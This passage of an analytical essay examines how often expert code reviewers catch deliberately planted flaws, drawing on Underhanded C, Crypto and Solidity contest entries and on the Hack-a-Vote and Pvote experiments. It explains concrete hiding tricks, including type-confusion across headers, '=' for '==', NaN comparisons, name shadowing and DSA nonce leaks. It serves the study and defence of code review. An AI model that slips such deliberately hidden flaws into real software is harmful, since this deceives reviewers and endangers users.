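# Deliberately hidden flaws in human-written code, and how often expert reviewers catch them

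## What code review does, and what changes when the author wants it to fail

In code review, someone other than the author reads a proposed change to a program to find faults before the project accepts the change. In 1976 Michael Fagan set out a formal version, in which reviewers met to inspect code together. Most organisations have since moved to a lighter form, in which each reviewer reads the change on a screen, in their own time, and leaves comments (Braz, Aeberhard and colleagues, *Less is More*, 2022).

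Code review developed around honest authors, who want to know about their mistakes. But some people have deliberately written harmful code that looks correct to a skilled reader, sometimes for a prize or an experiment and sometimes to attack widely used software. How often do expert reviewers catch such code?

How often reviewers catch hidden flaws also matters for AI oversight. People who expect humans to supervise AI systems often assume that checking a piece of work is easier than producing it. Deliberately hidden flaws test that assumption under hard conditions, because the producer wants the check to fail. The difference in ability between the producer and the checker is called the generator–verifier gap, and people disagree about how far it favours the checker.

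### How a change gets into a program

To change a program, a programmer edits a copy of its source code, the text from which a computer builds the running program, and sends the project a patch, which contains the proposed change and a description of its purpose. Reviewers mostly read a diff, which shows the lines the patch removes and adds, with a little of the surrounding code. They see the rest of the program, which may run to millions of lines, only if they open it themselves. A maintainer, someone with authority to accept changes and publish releases, decides whether to accept the patch. Once the project records the patch in its history, programmers call it a commit.

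In Google's account of its own practice, the author uploads a change, reviewers comment on the diff, and the author uploads new versions until a reviewer marks the change "looks good to me". By default, the change needs this mark from only one other engineer. It also needs approval from an owner of that part of the code and from someone qualified in the programming language, but the author can fill both of those roles. Google asks authors to keep small changes to about 200 lines and expects reviewers to respond within 24 working hours. Most changes get one reviewer, because in Google's experience the first approval matters most and further reviewers soon take more effort than they are worth.

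Review of the Linux kernel, the core of a widely used operating system, has more layers. According to the Linux kernel documentation's *How the development process works*, an author posts a patch to a public mailing list, where other developers comment. The maintainer of a subsystem, such as networking, may then take the patch into a separate copy of the code. The patch next goes into a combined test version, and then into the main version, which only Linus Torvalds can change. He cannot read everything, because a typical release contains about 13,000 changes, which arrive at close to 1,000 a day in the busiest two weeks. For one older release, 2.6.38, Torvalds directly chose 112 of more than 9,500 patches. For the rest he relied on the subsystem maintainers, who rely in turn on the maintainers below them, an arrangement kernel developers call a "chain of trust".

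After review, many projects publish a release tarball, an archive of the source code from which distributors build the version users install. The tarball can differ from the public repository that reviewers read, and the attacker behind the 2024 backdoor in the xz compression software exploited that difference.

### What reviewers look for, and what they take on trust

*Towards Practical Defect-Focused Automated Code Review* (2025) cites a survey of 165 managers and 873 programmers at Microsoft in which the main reason given for code review was finding defects. Reviewers at Google check whether a change has proper tests, a sound design and the right behaviour, but Google considers the main benefit of review to be ensuring that other engineers can understand the code and maintain it for years.

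*A Roadmap on Modern Code Review* (2024) puts security at about 1% of review comments. The figure may be slightly low, since reviewers often describe a security problem as questionable logic or weak code without calling it a vulnerability (a fault that an attacker can use). *Following Dragons* (2026) makes this point and adds that projects sometimes merge patches while a security concern is still open.

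Reviewers also assume that the author means well. Google tells its reviewers to defer to the author's approach unless it is deficient, and says it has optimised the process around trust in its engineers "to do the right thing". The Linux kernel documentation's *Researcher Guidelines* express the same assumption in terms of consent, stating that kernel developers have agreed to receive good-faith contributions but not intentionally flawed ones. The assumption is sensible, because a reviewer who treated every patch as a possible attack would review far fewer of them and insult many honest contributors.

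An author who wants to get a flaw past the reviewer can exploit each of these habits. The author writes the description explaining the change's purpose and decides how to divide the work. Google acknowledges that a set of small changes can be easy to understand one by one but hard to understand together. This makes even an honest colleague's work harder to review, and a dishonest author can use it to hide a flaw.

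The checks that follow review are also weaker against such an author. Before a release, kernel developers give most weight to regressions, in which something that used to work has stopped working. Accidental bugs often come to light this way. A competent backdoor breaks nothing, so users who don't know about it have no problem to report.

### Mistakes, underhanded code and backdoors

Here is an invented line in the programming language C, supposedly written to let administrators, and nobody else, open a restricted page:

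```c
if (user->role = ADMIN) open_page(user);
```

This line makes any user an administrator and then, as long as ADMIN is not zero, opens the page, because a single equals sign in C assigns a value. A hurried reader mistakes it for a comparison, which needs two equals signs, and takes the line to mean "if the user's role is administrator, open the page". *Initial Analysis of Underhanded Source Code* (Wheeler, 2020), a study for the US nonprofit Institute for Defense Analyses, describes an attacker's attempt in 2003 to insert the same one-character change into the Linux kernel.

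Programmers also make this slip by accident, so the line above could be an honest mistake or underhanded code, which is source code that looks innocent to a reader but does something harmful. The code is the same either way, and a diff doesn't show the author's intention. Entrants in the Underhanded C Contest try to write such code, in programs that are as "readable, clear, innocent and straightforward as possible" but fail to do their apparent job.

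Obfuscated code is different because a reviewer can see at once that it is hard to read. Wheeler leaves it out of his study because a reviewer can distrust it for that reason alone.

A backdoor is a deliberately hidden function that gives access or control to those who know of it. The word describes what the code does and leaves open how the code looks. Kokkonis, Marcozzi and colleagues (2025), in *ROSA*, give the example of a few extra lines in sudo, a tool that runs commands with another user's privileges. The lines make the program accept the password "let_me_in" from anyone. No programmer who read them would be fooled, so this backdoor lasts only while nobody looks. Underhanded code, for its part, need not be a backdoor at all, since a program that quietly miscounts votes gives nobody access to anything. (Kokkonis and colleagues also count a forgotten debugging login as an unintentional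 backdoor. Here the word covers deliberate ones only.)

A planted flaw can also have plausible deniability, meaning that it still looks like an honest mistake after someone finds it. Scott Craver, who first organised the Underhanded C Contest, praised a 2009 entry for this in *The 6th Underhanded C Contest is now Open* (2013). The flaw was one missing character, and the code around it was clumsy enough that a reader who spotted the error would take it for a beginner's mistake.

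### The catch rate and its missing denominator

The natural measure of a reviewer's success against planted flaws is the catch rate:

catch rate = planted flaws identified before acceptance ÷ planted flaws submitted

An experimenter who plants the flaws can calculate what share of them reviewers catch. In *Why Don't Developers Detect Improper Input Validation?*, Braz, Fregnan and colleagues (2021) gave 146 people, most of them working developers, a code change that contained one of two security flaws. On a first reading, 66 of them (45%) found the flaw.

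That figure is for a single reviewer, and a project may use several. If two reviewers each had a 45% chance of catching a flaw, and their chances were independent, at least one would catch it about 70% of the time (1 − 0.55²). That estimate is probably too high, because people with similar training tend to overlook similar things, and an author who plants a flaw will aim for those. Where one reviewer reads each change, as at Google, the single-reviewer figure applies.

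Records of real attacks can't show what share of planted flaws reviewers catch, because the total leaves out flaws that nobody has found. The count of caught flaws is also incomplete, though people mention this less often. A reviewer who rejects a planted flaw as an ordinary bug has stopped an attack without knowing it, so the catch isn't recorded as a stopped attack.

The two gaps bias the apparent catch rate in opposite directions. Suppose, hypothetically, that the public record holds ten planted flaws, of which reviewers caught four and other people found six after acceptance. The apparent catch rate is 40%, but the same record could result from very different true rates. If another 14 flaws got through and remain undiscovered, the true rate is 4 in 24, or 17%. If no flaws remain undiscovered, but reviewers rejected another 20 as ordinary bugs, the true rate is 24 in 30, or 80%.

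Reports of backdoors are also scarce, according to Kokkonis and colleagues, and many point to samples that no longer exist. Auditing a program for backdoors takes long, painstaking inspection, which they say often nobody does. Their test collection, which they describe as the largest used to evaluate backdoor detection, holds 17 backdoors, 10 of them synthetic. A list of famous attacks can therefore show that some kind of flaw can pass review, but not what share of such flaws do.

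### Four questions for every case

A single case can still be informative if we know whether a reviewer saw the flawed code, whether anyone had warned the reviewer, how much code there was and how much time to review it, and whether whoever found the flaw recognised it as deliberate.

A catch rate should count only flaws in code that reviewers saw. An intruder who alters a file on a project's server bypasses review, as does a maintainer who adds something only to the release tarball. Both are serious security failures, but including them in the rate would make reviewers look worse than they are.

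Warning reviewers has a large effect on detection, at least for some flaws. In the 2021 experiment, Braz and colleagues told the 80 people who had missed the flaw that the change contained a vulnerability, without saying what kind, and invited them to look again. Twenty then found it. In the 2022 experiment, they told some reviewers at the start to look for security problems in a change that contained two flaws. Of the 33 reviewers without this instruction, one found the first flaw (3%) and seven found the second (21%). Of the 41 with it, 19 found the first (46%) and 25 found the second (61%). The instruction roughly tripled the probability of finding the second flaw. Only one reviewer found the first flaw without the instruction, which is too few to support any multiple. The paper describes detection as eight times more probable with the instruction, but that figure is a ratio of odds.

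Neither warning suggested that the author might be hostile, so neither study tested the effect of that suspicion. Wheeler examined entries from a 2004 contest to write programs that miscount votes. He reported that the flaws could be hard to find even though he knew the programs were malicious and had the organisers' notes on how each one worked. In their notes on one entry, the organisers wrongly attributed the miscounting to a swap of the letter O for the digit 0, when the cause was a misused arithmetic operator further down in the code.

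How well a result applies to other settings depends on how much code the reviewers read and how much time they had. The changes in the two experiments were 137 to 160 lines long, close to what Google recommends, and each contained everything a reader needed to spot the flaw. A flaw that depends on how a new line interacts with old code elsewhere in a large program takes a reviewer much more work to find, and a volunteer maintainer with a day job may have less time to look.

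Recognising intent matters because an author who isn't suspected can keep trying. A reviewer who asks "shouldn't this be two equals signs?" has caught the flaw, and it counts towards the catch rate, but the author can fix the line and submit another flaw next month. Suppose reviewers catch 80% of planted flaws and never grow suspicious. An author who makes five independent attempts then has a 67% chance of getting at least one through (1 − 0.8⁵). If the first catch exposes the author as an attacker and ends their access, the chance stays at 20%.

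## Contests in writing innocent-looking malicious code

Since 2004, programmers have competed in public to write underhanded code. The contests have produced a large collection of flaws designed to get past reviewers, often with explanations of how they work.

### The vote counters of 2004

The earliest such contest that Wheeler found was the Obfuscated V Contest, which Daniel Horn ran around the 2004 US presidential election. In *Obfuscated Vote Counting Contest*, Horn (2004) traced the idea to a contest for unreadable C programs and to the "current E-voting scandals". Entrants wrote a program that appeared to count votes correctly but got the totals wrong in favour of one candidate. Despite the contest's name, Horn wanted underhanded code and told entrants that obviously incorrect programs were unwelcome.

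Under the rules in Horn's *The Obfuscated V contest*, judges inspected the programs by eye on election day and then ran the one that looked most correct. If it miscounted, it won; otherwise, the judges moved on to the next. One category was for programs that passed a test the day before and miscounted only on election day, and another was for programs that could miscount at any time. The prize was a CD of a computer game.

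Nine of the 40 entries that Wheeler later analysed were in the election-day category. The other 31 gave wrong answers on any date, so good tests would have exposed them without anyone reading the code. Michal Zalewski received the judges' highest score, 7.3 out of ten. His program used a macro, a piece of text that the C compiler pastes in wherever the macro's name appears. The pasted text created a variable called `t`, which hid an outer variable with the same name. As a result, about one vote in ten went to George W. Bush, whoever the voter had chosen.

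### The Underhanded C Contest

Scott Craver entered Horn's contest and started the Underhanded C Contest the following year. In its *FAQ*, he recalls being impressed that even a short program for counting characters could fail only on one specific day, which hides the bug during testing. He ran the contest from 2005 to 2009 and again from 2013 to 2015, with a new task each time.

In 2009 the task was to process airline luggage records so that an angry employee could make a record disappear by typing the right comment. The winner, Sam Blackburn, wrote a program that censored swear words in the comments. He left one comma out of his list of words and replacements. C joins neighbouring strings when no comma separates them, so the replacement for one four-letter word was nine characters long. The extra characters ran past the end of the comment and marked the record for deletion.

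The 2013 task was to write code that measured how closely two users of a social network were connected while secretly giving the attacker access to strangers. It drew more than 40 entries. The 2014 task was to write surveillance code that secretly alerted the people under surveillance, and it drew more than two dozen.

Craver (2014), in *The 7th Underhanded C Contest is now Open*, gave more points to short, readable programs, because a flaw is harder to hide in them. A visual slip, such as a letter l in place of the digit 1, counted as much as exploiting an obscure language feature. Entrants also gained points if the flaw was plausibly deniable and if it still looked innocent with syntax highlighting. Humour and spite earned extra points, so the winners weren't chosen for stealth alone.

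### A warhead detector that accepts fakes

The Nuclear Threat Initiative, a nonprofit that works to reduce the danger from weapons of mass destruction, helped design the task for the 2015 contest and sponsored a $1,000 prize. *Results of the 2015 Underhanded C Contest* (Craver, 2016) describes a scenario in which two invented countries have agreed to destroy nuclear warheads, and inspectors must confirm that each warhead contains real fissile material. A gamma-ray scan would show this but also reveal secrets of the weapon's design, so the countries agree to use a program that compares the scan with a trusted reference and outputs only "yes" or "no". Entrants had to write a comparison that worked in general but accepted a fake warhead under conditions the host country could arrange.

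About a third of the more than 40 entries relied on NaN ("not a number"), a special value produced by calculations such as zero divided by zero. The comparison "NaN is smaller than x" is false for every number x, so a program that rejects a warhead only if its score is below the threshold will accept one whose score is NaN. Few of these entries reached the shortlist, partly because experienced C programmers look out for unchecked divisions. Michael Dunphy added a check but left out a single `&`, so the check recorded the error in a private copy of a variable and never passed it to the rest of the program.

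Linus Åkesson won with 66 lines of code in three files. The first file, `match.h`, contains this line:

```c
typedef double float_t; /* Desired precision for floating-point vectors */
```

A reader would take `float_t` for a name that Åkesson had made up, and would believe that from here on it means `double`, an eight-byte number. The second file, `match.c`, includes `match.h`, so there the belief is correct. The third file does the actual comparison. These are its first line and the line that opens its main function:

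```c
#include <math.h> /* sqrt */
...
double spectral_contrast(float_t *a, float_t *b, int length)
```

The function scales both spectra to a standard size and returns a score for how well they match. Its file includes only `math.h`, a standard C header, and not `match.h`. The comment gives an innocent reason for this, which is that the program needs a square root. But `math.h` also defines `float_t`, on most machines as `float`, a four-byte number. A C compiler processes each file separately, so it did not compare the two definitions and reported no conflict. As a result, `match.c` passes arrays of eight-byte numbers to `spectral_contrast`, which reads them as four-byte numbers.

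The function reads as many numbers as `match.c` specifies, but at half the width, so it stops halfway through the array and ignores the right half of the spectrum. It also reads each `double` as two `float` values. Gamma-ray detectors count individual events, so the numbers are whole and fairly small. The lower half of each `double` is therefore all zeros, which match in any two spectra.

The misreading heavily compresses the upper half of each `double`. A `double` uses 11 bits for its exponent, the power of two that sets the number's size, while a `float` uses only 8. Three exponent bits are therefore read as part of the fraction, which Åkesson explains is roughly the same as taking the eighth root. A stored 10 becomes about 2.56 and a stored 1,000 becomes about 4.48, so a hundredfold difference shrinks to less than twofold. Åkesson designed the earlier smoothing steps to keep the lower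 halves at zero, for example by averaging over 16 values, a power of two.

As a result, the program checks where the peaks are in the left half of the spectrum and almost ignores how high they are. A cheating country could leave a little of the real material in the warhead and add another radioactive substance with a strong peak on the right. The added substance also lets the fake pass a separate check on total radiation, which Åkesson's documentation presents as a safeguard against this kind of fraud.

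He simulated 1,000 fakes that were 10% genuine material. Many failed, but a country could choose the best one. The example he printed passes at any threshold up to 0.72, and his documentation recommended 0.6. The trick doesn't work on 32-bit x86 Linux, where `float_t` has yet another meaning.

Craver observed that a reader who misses the confusion over the type will find nothing else in the program even slightly suspicious. A reader who does notice it will see what looks like a forgotten `#include`. Testing would have been more likely than reading to expose the flaw. Given two spectra of similar total strength that differ only towards the right-hand end, the flawed program would probably report a match, and a tester who tried this would know that something was wrong.

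Two earlier winners used a similar mismatch. In 2013 Alex Olson's 54-line program declared a function in one file as writing an `int` and defined it in another as writing a `long`, which can be twice as wide. The extra bytes overwrote the number that recorded how closely two users were connected, so an account named "!!!" with no friends got the closest possible connection to everyone. The 2007 winner declared the standard function `time()` incorrectly. To find the flaw in any of the three programs, a reviewer has to compare declarations in different files, but a diff may show only one of those files.

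### Why the contests give no catch rate

The Nuclear Threat Initiative's *"Underhanded C" Contest Highlights Challenges For Nuclear Arms Control Verification Technologies* drew the lesson from such entries that arms control has no standards for writing or reviewing this kind of software, which is a narrower claim than that expert review doesn't work. Craver writes in the Underhanded C Contest's FAQ that "we need more code review, not less".

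The contests show that people can write malicious programs of about 60 lines that look ordinary. The results can't be used to estimate how often reviewers miss such programs, because the public sees mainly the successes. The Underhanded C website describes the winners, the runners-up and a few other entries. Wheeler asked for the complete set of entries but had not received it when he published.

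The judges also knew that every entry was malicious. This made their task easier than a maintainer's in one respect, because they never had to decide whether to be suspicious. The contests included no honest programs, so nobody learned how often the judges would have accused an honest author.

In 2015, Craver asked entrants to put their explanations in a separate file so that the judges could first read each program in "complete ignorance" of the trick. If the judges had recorded whether they found the flaw on that first reading, the contest would have measured how often warned experts catch flaws in short programs, but the published results contain no such count.

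There are only anecdotes about how often expert reviewers catch the flaws in contest entries. Craver (2015), in *2014 Winners*, admits that he spent some time staring at a very short entry by Domenico Andriole without finding the bug. It was in a function that saved the user's profile picture. Andriole had left out the function's body and mentioned the download only in a comment, and that download could alert the user to the surveillance. Reading the visible code more carefully would not have helped.

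Comments misled readers in other contests too. The JavaScript Misdirection Contest of 2015 received 40 entries, of which 34 were valid, and many of them leaked a secret key by placing it in the address of an image. According to Wheeler, several entrants put a link to Stack Overflow, a site where programmers answer each other's questions, in a comment above the strange code. The organiser thought this clever, because he was used to comments that explain unusual code, and he found it easier to skip over code with a good comment above it. (A similar contest for the language Rust, announced in December 2016, never published any entries.)

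Hiding a flaw in a contest entry is also easier in some ways than getting one past ordinary review, and harder in others. An entrant can design a whole program around the flaw, while an attacker who sends a patch has to work with code that other people wrote. But the contest scoring rewards brevity, whereas an attacker can bury a flaw in a long and tedious change.

### Forty samples and five countermeasures

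Wheeler interpreted the evidence more hopefully in a 2020 study. He closely analyzed the Obfuscated V entries because they were the earliest public set, and Horn had published every entry the judges scored, so the set avoids the worst of the selection problem.

Wheeler first had to correct the organisers' notes on four entries. One was the misattributed letter O described earlier. The organisers blamed a strange compiler command for the miscounting in another, but they had not recorded the command, and the program was harmless without it. They described the trick in a third as "gets instead of equals", which Wheeler took to mean `=` in place of `==`, since the program never uses the C function `gets`. The trick they described for the fourth was missing from the published program, which appeared to count votes correctly, so Wheeler dropped that entry, leaving 40.

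Twenty-five of the 40 (62.5%) fell into five familiar patterns:

| Pattern | Samples | How it misleads a reader |
|---|---|---|
| Misused macros | 9 | Pasted-in text changes the meaning of an ordinary-looking line |
| Confusable characters | 7 | A variable named l or O looks like the digit 1 or 0 |
| Memory overflow | 5 | The program reads or writes past the end of an array |
| Code in an apparent comment | 2 | The comment ends earlier than the layout suggests |
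| `=` for `==` | 2 | The program changes a value where the reader sees a comparison |

Honest programmers make many of these mistakes by accident, so tools for finding accidents might find the deliberate versions too. Wheeler selected five countermeasures:

- run the program with Address Sanitizer, a tool that detects improper use of memory
- restrict macros sharply
- forbid names that use a lowercase l or an uppercase O where someone could confuse them with digits
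- colour the code by type and reformat it so that no live code can follow a comment on the same line
- turn on a long list of warnings in gcc, a widely used C compiler.

Of the 40 samples, 30 (75%) were caught by at least one of the five. Another should have triggered gcc's warning about misleading indentation, but didn't because of an apparent bug in gcc, which Wheeler reported. He judged that six of the remaining nine would make a human reviewer suspicious, for instance because of odd repetition or very unusual constructions. That left three (7.5%) that were neither detectable nor suspicious, or four including the one that gcc missed.

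The flaws in these three programs look like small mistakes. Jared Sohn's program checks twice whether a vote is "n", when the second check should be for a capital "N". Matthew Russotto's fills in only part of a table because it measures the length of the wrong table, and Robert Seace's converts a number to the wrong type. Wheeler thought that additional compiler warnings could catch such cases.

In his table, the contest judges' scores for these three programs, which got past the tools, are 5.3, 4.3 and 3.7. At least one countermeasure defeated each of the four highest-scoring entries, which scored 6.7 to 7.3. He doesn't make this comparison himself. The sample is small, but the difference is a reason to use both human reviewers and tools.

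Wheeler anticipated the objection that he had chosen his countermeasures after seeing the samples. He replied that he only wanted to show that a small set of simple, general measures can often detect underhanded code. The method is reasonable for that purpose, but the 75% figure is less useful as a forecast, because measures fitted to one set of programs will usually do worse on the next.

The figure also depends heavily on his judgement. The only countermeasure he reports running on every sample is gcc, which caught 15 by a count of his table. For the rest, he worked out what a tool or rule would do. He didn't have time to run Address Sanitizer on every program, and his study had no tool for detecting confusable letters. Most of his assessments are easy to believe. For example, a ban on variables called `l` stops a trick that needs one. His classification of six programs as "suspicious"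 is less reliable, because he already knew that they were malicious. He had also written two of the 40 programs. One triggered a gcc warning, and he classed the other as suspicious.

We don't know how many false alarms the countermeasures would raise, because Wheeler didn't test them on honest programs for comparison. False alarms matter because a reviewer who sees dozens of harmless warnings every day may stop reading them. Many entries did trigger gcc warnings for unrelated mistakes, but Wheeler rightly didn't count these as detections, since an author could fix the mistakes and leave the flaw in place.

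The largest gap is that nobody in 2004 was trying to beat Wheeler's countermeasures. An attacker who knows that a project uses gcc can run it first and revise the code until the relevant warning disappears. Some warnings are very easy to avoid. With the settings Wheeler used, gcc warns about a single equals sign in a condition unless extra parentheses surround the assignment, and the attacker who targeted the Linux kernel in 2003 had included those parentheses. Wheeler suggested that projects keep the details of some countermeasures private so that attackers can't prepare for all of them. He also argued that the measures only need to be good enough to deter an attacker, who has to write code that does a specific wrong thing while appearing to do the right one.

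Åkesson's program gives a rough idea of how the five countermeasures would do on a better entry, though Wheeler didn't try them on it. It has no memory overflow, confusable names or hidden code, and its only macro is a harmless constant, so four of the countermeasures would probably find nothing. The fifth might find something, because one of the gcc options on Wheeler's list warns when a program stores a `double` in a `float`, and the comparison file does this when it divides each value. That warning would have given a reviewer who believed that `float_t` meant `double` a reason to look again.

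Syntax highlighting is a weaker defence than it sounds. Wheeler describes a Python program that exploits `//`, which starts a comment in many languages but means division in Python. This wouldn't fool someone who knew only Python, but most professionals know several languages. Wheeler missed the trick even though his editor coloured the line correctly.

He found that the flaws became easier to spot as he worked through the collection, and he suggested training reviewers on samples. He acknowledged that this could also be because the entries were in order from hardest to easiest.

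### Cryptography and the need for specialists

The Underhanded Crypto Contest, which ran from 2014 to 2018, invited people to design a system that "looks secure to experts" but has a subtle backdoor or weakness, according to the rules quoted by ianG (2014) in *Underhanded Crypto*. Adam Caudill and Taylor Hornby ran the contest, and judging was slow. Caudill (2015), in *On the Underhanded Crypto Contest*, reports that they announced the first winners, John Meacham and Gaëtan Leurent, two months late. The Crypto & Privacy Village hosted a smaller round at the Def Con security conference in 2015. Its slides list eight judges, and the lessons include using a simpler process with fewer judges.

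That smaller round received five entries. Its two tasks, described in Hornby's *Second Underhanded Crypto Contest*, were to make the encryption program GnuPG leak a user's private key and to put a backdoor in a password system. Joseph Birr-Pixton won the GnuPG category by exploiting how the program chose random numbers for digital signatures.

The mathematics shows why an ordinary reviewer would struggle. GnuPG can sign messages with a method called DSA, which uses a long-term private key *x* and a fresh secret number *k* for each signature. The signature consists of two numbers, *r* and *s*. If *h* is a number computed from the message, then

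s = k⁻¹(h + x·r) mod q

where *q* is a public prime number and "mod q" means that only the remainder after division by *q* counts. Anyone who sees the message and its signature knows *h*, *r* and *s*. If they also learn *k*, they can rearrange the equation and compute the private key:

x = (s·k − h)·r⁻¹ mod q

Attackers may not even need all of *k*, since numbers that are not random enough can also reveal the key. The signatures are still valid, so an ordinary test that creates a signature and checks it will pass.

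A reviewer who doesn't know the cryptographic weakness being exploited sees only a change to how the program picks a number. The C code itself may contain no errors, so compiler warnings and memory checks won't catch the flaw. Wheeler didn't analyse the cryptography entries in detail, but noted that many winners exploited highly technical weaknesses of this sort. He concluded that specialists must review such code in depth. Simple countermeasures could still help indirectly by ruling out easier tricks, which would give reviewers more time to understand what the software does.

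### Solidity and changes to the language

Solidity is a language for smart contracts, programs that hold and transfer money on the Ethereum blockchain. Unlike reviewers, its developers can change the language so that a trick stops working. The first Underhanded Solidity contest, in 2017, showed its results directly to them. Its judges included Christian Reitwiessner, the language's lead developer, according to the announcement that Stalder (2017) forwarded to a mailing list.

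Many entries in 2017 used shadowing, in which a program reuses the name of something built into the language. ConsenSys gives the example of `revert()`, which normally cancels a transaction in Solidity. A contract could define its own `revert()` that does nothing, and a reader who saw the call would wrongly assume that the transaction stopped there.

The contest didn't prompt the first warnings about shadowing, which the developers had added shortly before it. But Wheeler quotes Reitwiessner as saying afterwards that the solution was incomplete and that work on it continued. Wheeler also reports that the team went on to refine the language and its compiler. The team also found that an automated solver could detect some of the attacks. Another common trick, sending money to a contract without triggering the code that keeps its accounts, was harder to remove, and Reitwiessner called it "quite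 tricky" to address through the language.

The contest returned in 2020, when entrants wrote contracts whose owners could later replace the code. The judges were to receive anonymised entries (Solidity, 2020). One entry illustrated that an audit is worthless unless someone also checks every later upgrade. Another hid its flaw well by exploiting a bug in the compiler itself, but the judges thought that the code around it "would raise eyebrows" (Solidity, 2020).

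*Announcing the Winners of the Underhanded Solidity Contest 2022* (Heintel, 2022) lists finding faults in the language's design among the contest's aims, and *Announcing the Winners of the Underhanded Solidity Contest 2024* (Mehta, 2024) adds testing new features and restrictions. Entrants in these later rounds could study the defences before writing their entries, unlike those in Horn's 2004 contest.

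The 2022 winner, ChainSecurity engineer Tynan, used a little-known quirk in Solidity to build a harmless-looking but malicious currency exchange (ChainSecurity, *Beware of Undefined Behavior!*, 2022). He had analysed the quirk for his thesis at ETH Zurich. A reviewer could learn to recognise a fake `revert()` in a minute, but few people had the knowledge needed to spot Tynan's flaw. Nobody has measured whether the earlier warnings pushed entrants towards such obscure tricks.

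## Experiments in which reviewers looked for planted flaws

In 2003, students in a graduate computer security class at Rice University hid flaws in a voting program and then searched one another's versions for them. Their instructors recorded how many of the flaws the searchers found, a count that the contests lack.

### Hack-a-Vote

The program, called Hack-a-Vote, was about 2,000 lines of Java that imitated the paperless voting machines American election officials were then adopting. A voter entered a PIN, chose candidates and confirmed the choices. When the election closed, the program shuffled the ballots, so that nobody could match them to voters, and counted them. The instructors had built it to show how easily a programmer could rig such a machine, and their own version included about 150 lines, all in one file, that rigged the election. They removed those lines before giving the program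 to the class.

The twelve students worked in pairs, which would make six pairs. Each pair first played developers whom a criminal organisation had paid to rig an election without getting caught, and had two weeks to alter the program. The pairs then became auditors, and each had one week to find the security flaws in the altered programs of two other pairs.

The auditors could not run a tool such as `diff` to compare an altered program with the original, because it would have shown them the changes. In that respect their task was harder than ordinary code review, where the reviewer starts from a diff. But they had spent two weeks with the clean program and could compare from memory, which the instructors called a limited "mental diff". It also helped that the code was short, tidy and well commented, and that the rules forbade anyone to rewrite a major part of it. However, the auditors were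 students with other work, and could not spend eight hours a day on the search.

Many pairs designed their hacks to survive testing. One pair gave extra votes to a chosen party, but only on terminals numbered above two, guessing that testers would set up at most two machines. Another pair's hack took effect only after a certain number of people had voted. Several pairs created ways to bypass the PIN check. Some made the program accept 10 or 1776 as a PIN, since both numbers already appeared in the code for innocent reasons and would not look out of place.

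Other pairs exploited features of Java. One gave a variable the same name as a class, so a line that seemed to call the class's vote-saving method called a substitute method instead. Another made an invalid PIN trigger an error in the program's network code, and the error made the program skip the check on the next PIN.

A subtler hack made one candidate disappear from the results. The program counted votes in a table with an entry for each candidate. Java calls two small methods, `hashCode()` and `equals()`, to check whether two candidates share an entry, and a programmer can rewrite both. One pair rewrote them, without needing to change the counting code, so that two candidates counted as the same person if one name began with the other. In a race between Robert Green and Robert Greenwood, for example, one of them would receive both men's votes and the other would not be listed.

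Two pairs audited each altered program. Both pairs found about two thirds of the hacks, and only one hack was missed by both. That hack was an option, set when the voting terminal started up, that disrupted the terminal's connection to the console that checked PINs.

Sometimes the auditors found a hack but misjudged what it did. This happened with the disappearing candidate, although a bug in the hack itself may have confused them. It isn't obvious whether such a find should count as a catch. A maintainer who rejects a strange `equals()` method has stopped the attack, even without understanding it. But the attack gets through if the maintainer asks about the method and accepts a plausible answer, which someone who writes underhanded code will usually have ready.

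### What a second pair of auditors adds

The Rice results give the share of hacks that both pairs found, but a project with one set of auditors needs to know how often a single pair succeeds. Suppose that every pair had the same chance *p* of finding any given hack, and that the two pairs' chances were independent. Then

p² = 2/3, so p ≈ 0.82

(1 − p)² ≈ 0.03

On these assumptions one pair would catch about 82% of the hacks, and both pairs would miss about 3%.

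The estimate for a single pair hardly depends on independence. A pair's average catch rate is the share of hacks that both pairs found, plus half the share that only one of them found. If *m* is the share that neither found, the average is

2/3 + ½(1/3 − m) = 5/6 − m/2

The instructors described well over a dozen hacks, and both pairs missed one of them, so *m* was probably between 5% and 8%. The average is therefore about 80%, whether or not the pairs tended to miss the same hacks.

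The 3% is much less certain, because it assumes that every hack was equally hard to find. Suppose instead that each pair has only a 20% chance of catching any hack in the hardest tenth, and an 86% chance of catching any other. The share of hacks found by both pairs would still be two thirds (0.9 × 0.86² + 0.1 × 0.2² ≈ 0.67), as it was at Rice, but the share missed by both would be 8%. The collection is so small that a single undetected hack fits either assumption.

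The difference grows as a project adds reviewers. If five pairs worked independently and all hacks were equally hard to find, about one hack in 5,000 would get past all five pairs. In the mixed case, where a tenth of the hacks are difficult, about one in 30 would, and nearly all of those would come from the difficult tenth. Adding reviewers helps little if they tend to miss the same hacks, as the Rice students may have, since they had attended the same course and studied the same clean program.

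In the mixed example, the average catch rate over all hacks is about 80%, but if an attacker submitted only the difficult kind, one pair would catch 20% of them and two pairs would catch 36%.

The instructors doubted that auditors would do as well on a real voting machine. The code for machines made by Diebold, a large manufacturer, had more than 50,000 lines, at least 25 times as many as Hack-a-Vote. An employee of the company that had independently reviewed Diebold's code thought a hack hidden in it would have a 99.9% chance of going undetected. That figure seems to be an opinion, and the Rice exercise can't confirm it because every pair worked on a program of the same size.

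### Pvote and the untrusted author

In 2007, at the University of California, Berkeley, Ka-Ping Yee and David Wagner asked reviewers to search much less code, the roughly 460 lines of a voting program called Pvote. They planted a flaw in it for part of the review. Wagner later described the conditions in Financial Cryptography's *The Ka-Ping challenge* (2013), where he invited the public to try the same task.

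The reviewers knew that the program contained at least one bug, in a marked region of 100 lines. They had a description of the program's design and a long document arguing, step by step, that the original version was secure. They could also question the authors during the review.

To imitate an insider attack, Yee and Wagner told the reviewers to treat them as "untrusted adversaries" who might not always tell the truth. But they promised, to save time, to answer honestly any factual question that the reviewers could in principle check mechanically or in an independent source, such as how a Python command behaves or what the program did when it ran. They did not promise honest answers about why they had written a line in a particular way.

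The Pvote rule is nearly the reverse of ordinary practice, in which reviewers assume that the author means well. It makes sense wherever the author may be hostile, because it lets reviewers use the author's knowledge of the code without relying on the author's honesty.

Pvote also differed from a contest entry in that its authors first wrote it to be as secure and as easy to verify as they could, and added the flaw only afterwards. They therefore could not design the rest of the program around the flaw. However, they chose one that would pass the usual pre-election test, in which officials cast a few ballots, typically with at least one vote for each candidate, and check the totals. The reviewers therefore had to find it by reading the code.

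Wagner kept the answer secret and did not say how the original reviewers had done, so the challenge provides no catch rate. It is still a useful benchmark for how much help a reviewer can have. Experts who missed a flaw under these conditions would be unlikely to catch it in ordinary work, but success would be only weak evidence that they could find one in a long patch from a trusted colleague without being told that anything was wrong.

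### Two flaws with the same cause

In a 2021 experiment, Braz and colleagues put reviewers in that more usual position by saying that they wanted to improve code review, without mentioning security. The reviewers read a change to a system for managing employees' holidays, and 45% of them found the planted flaw on a first reading. This average combines two very different results.

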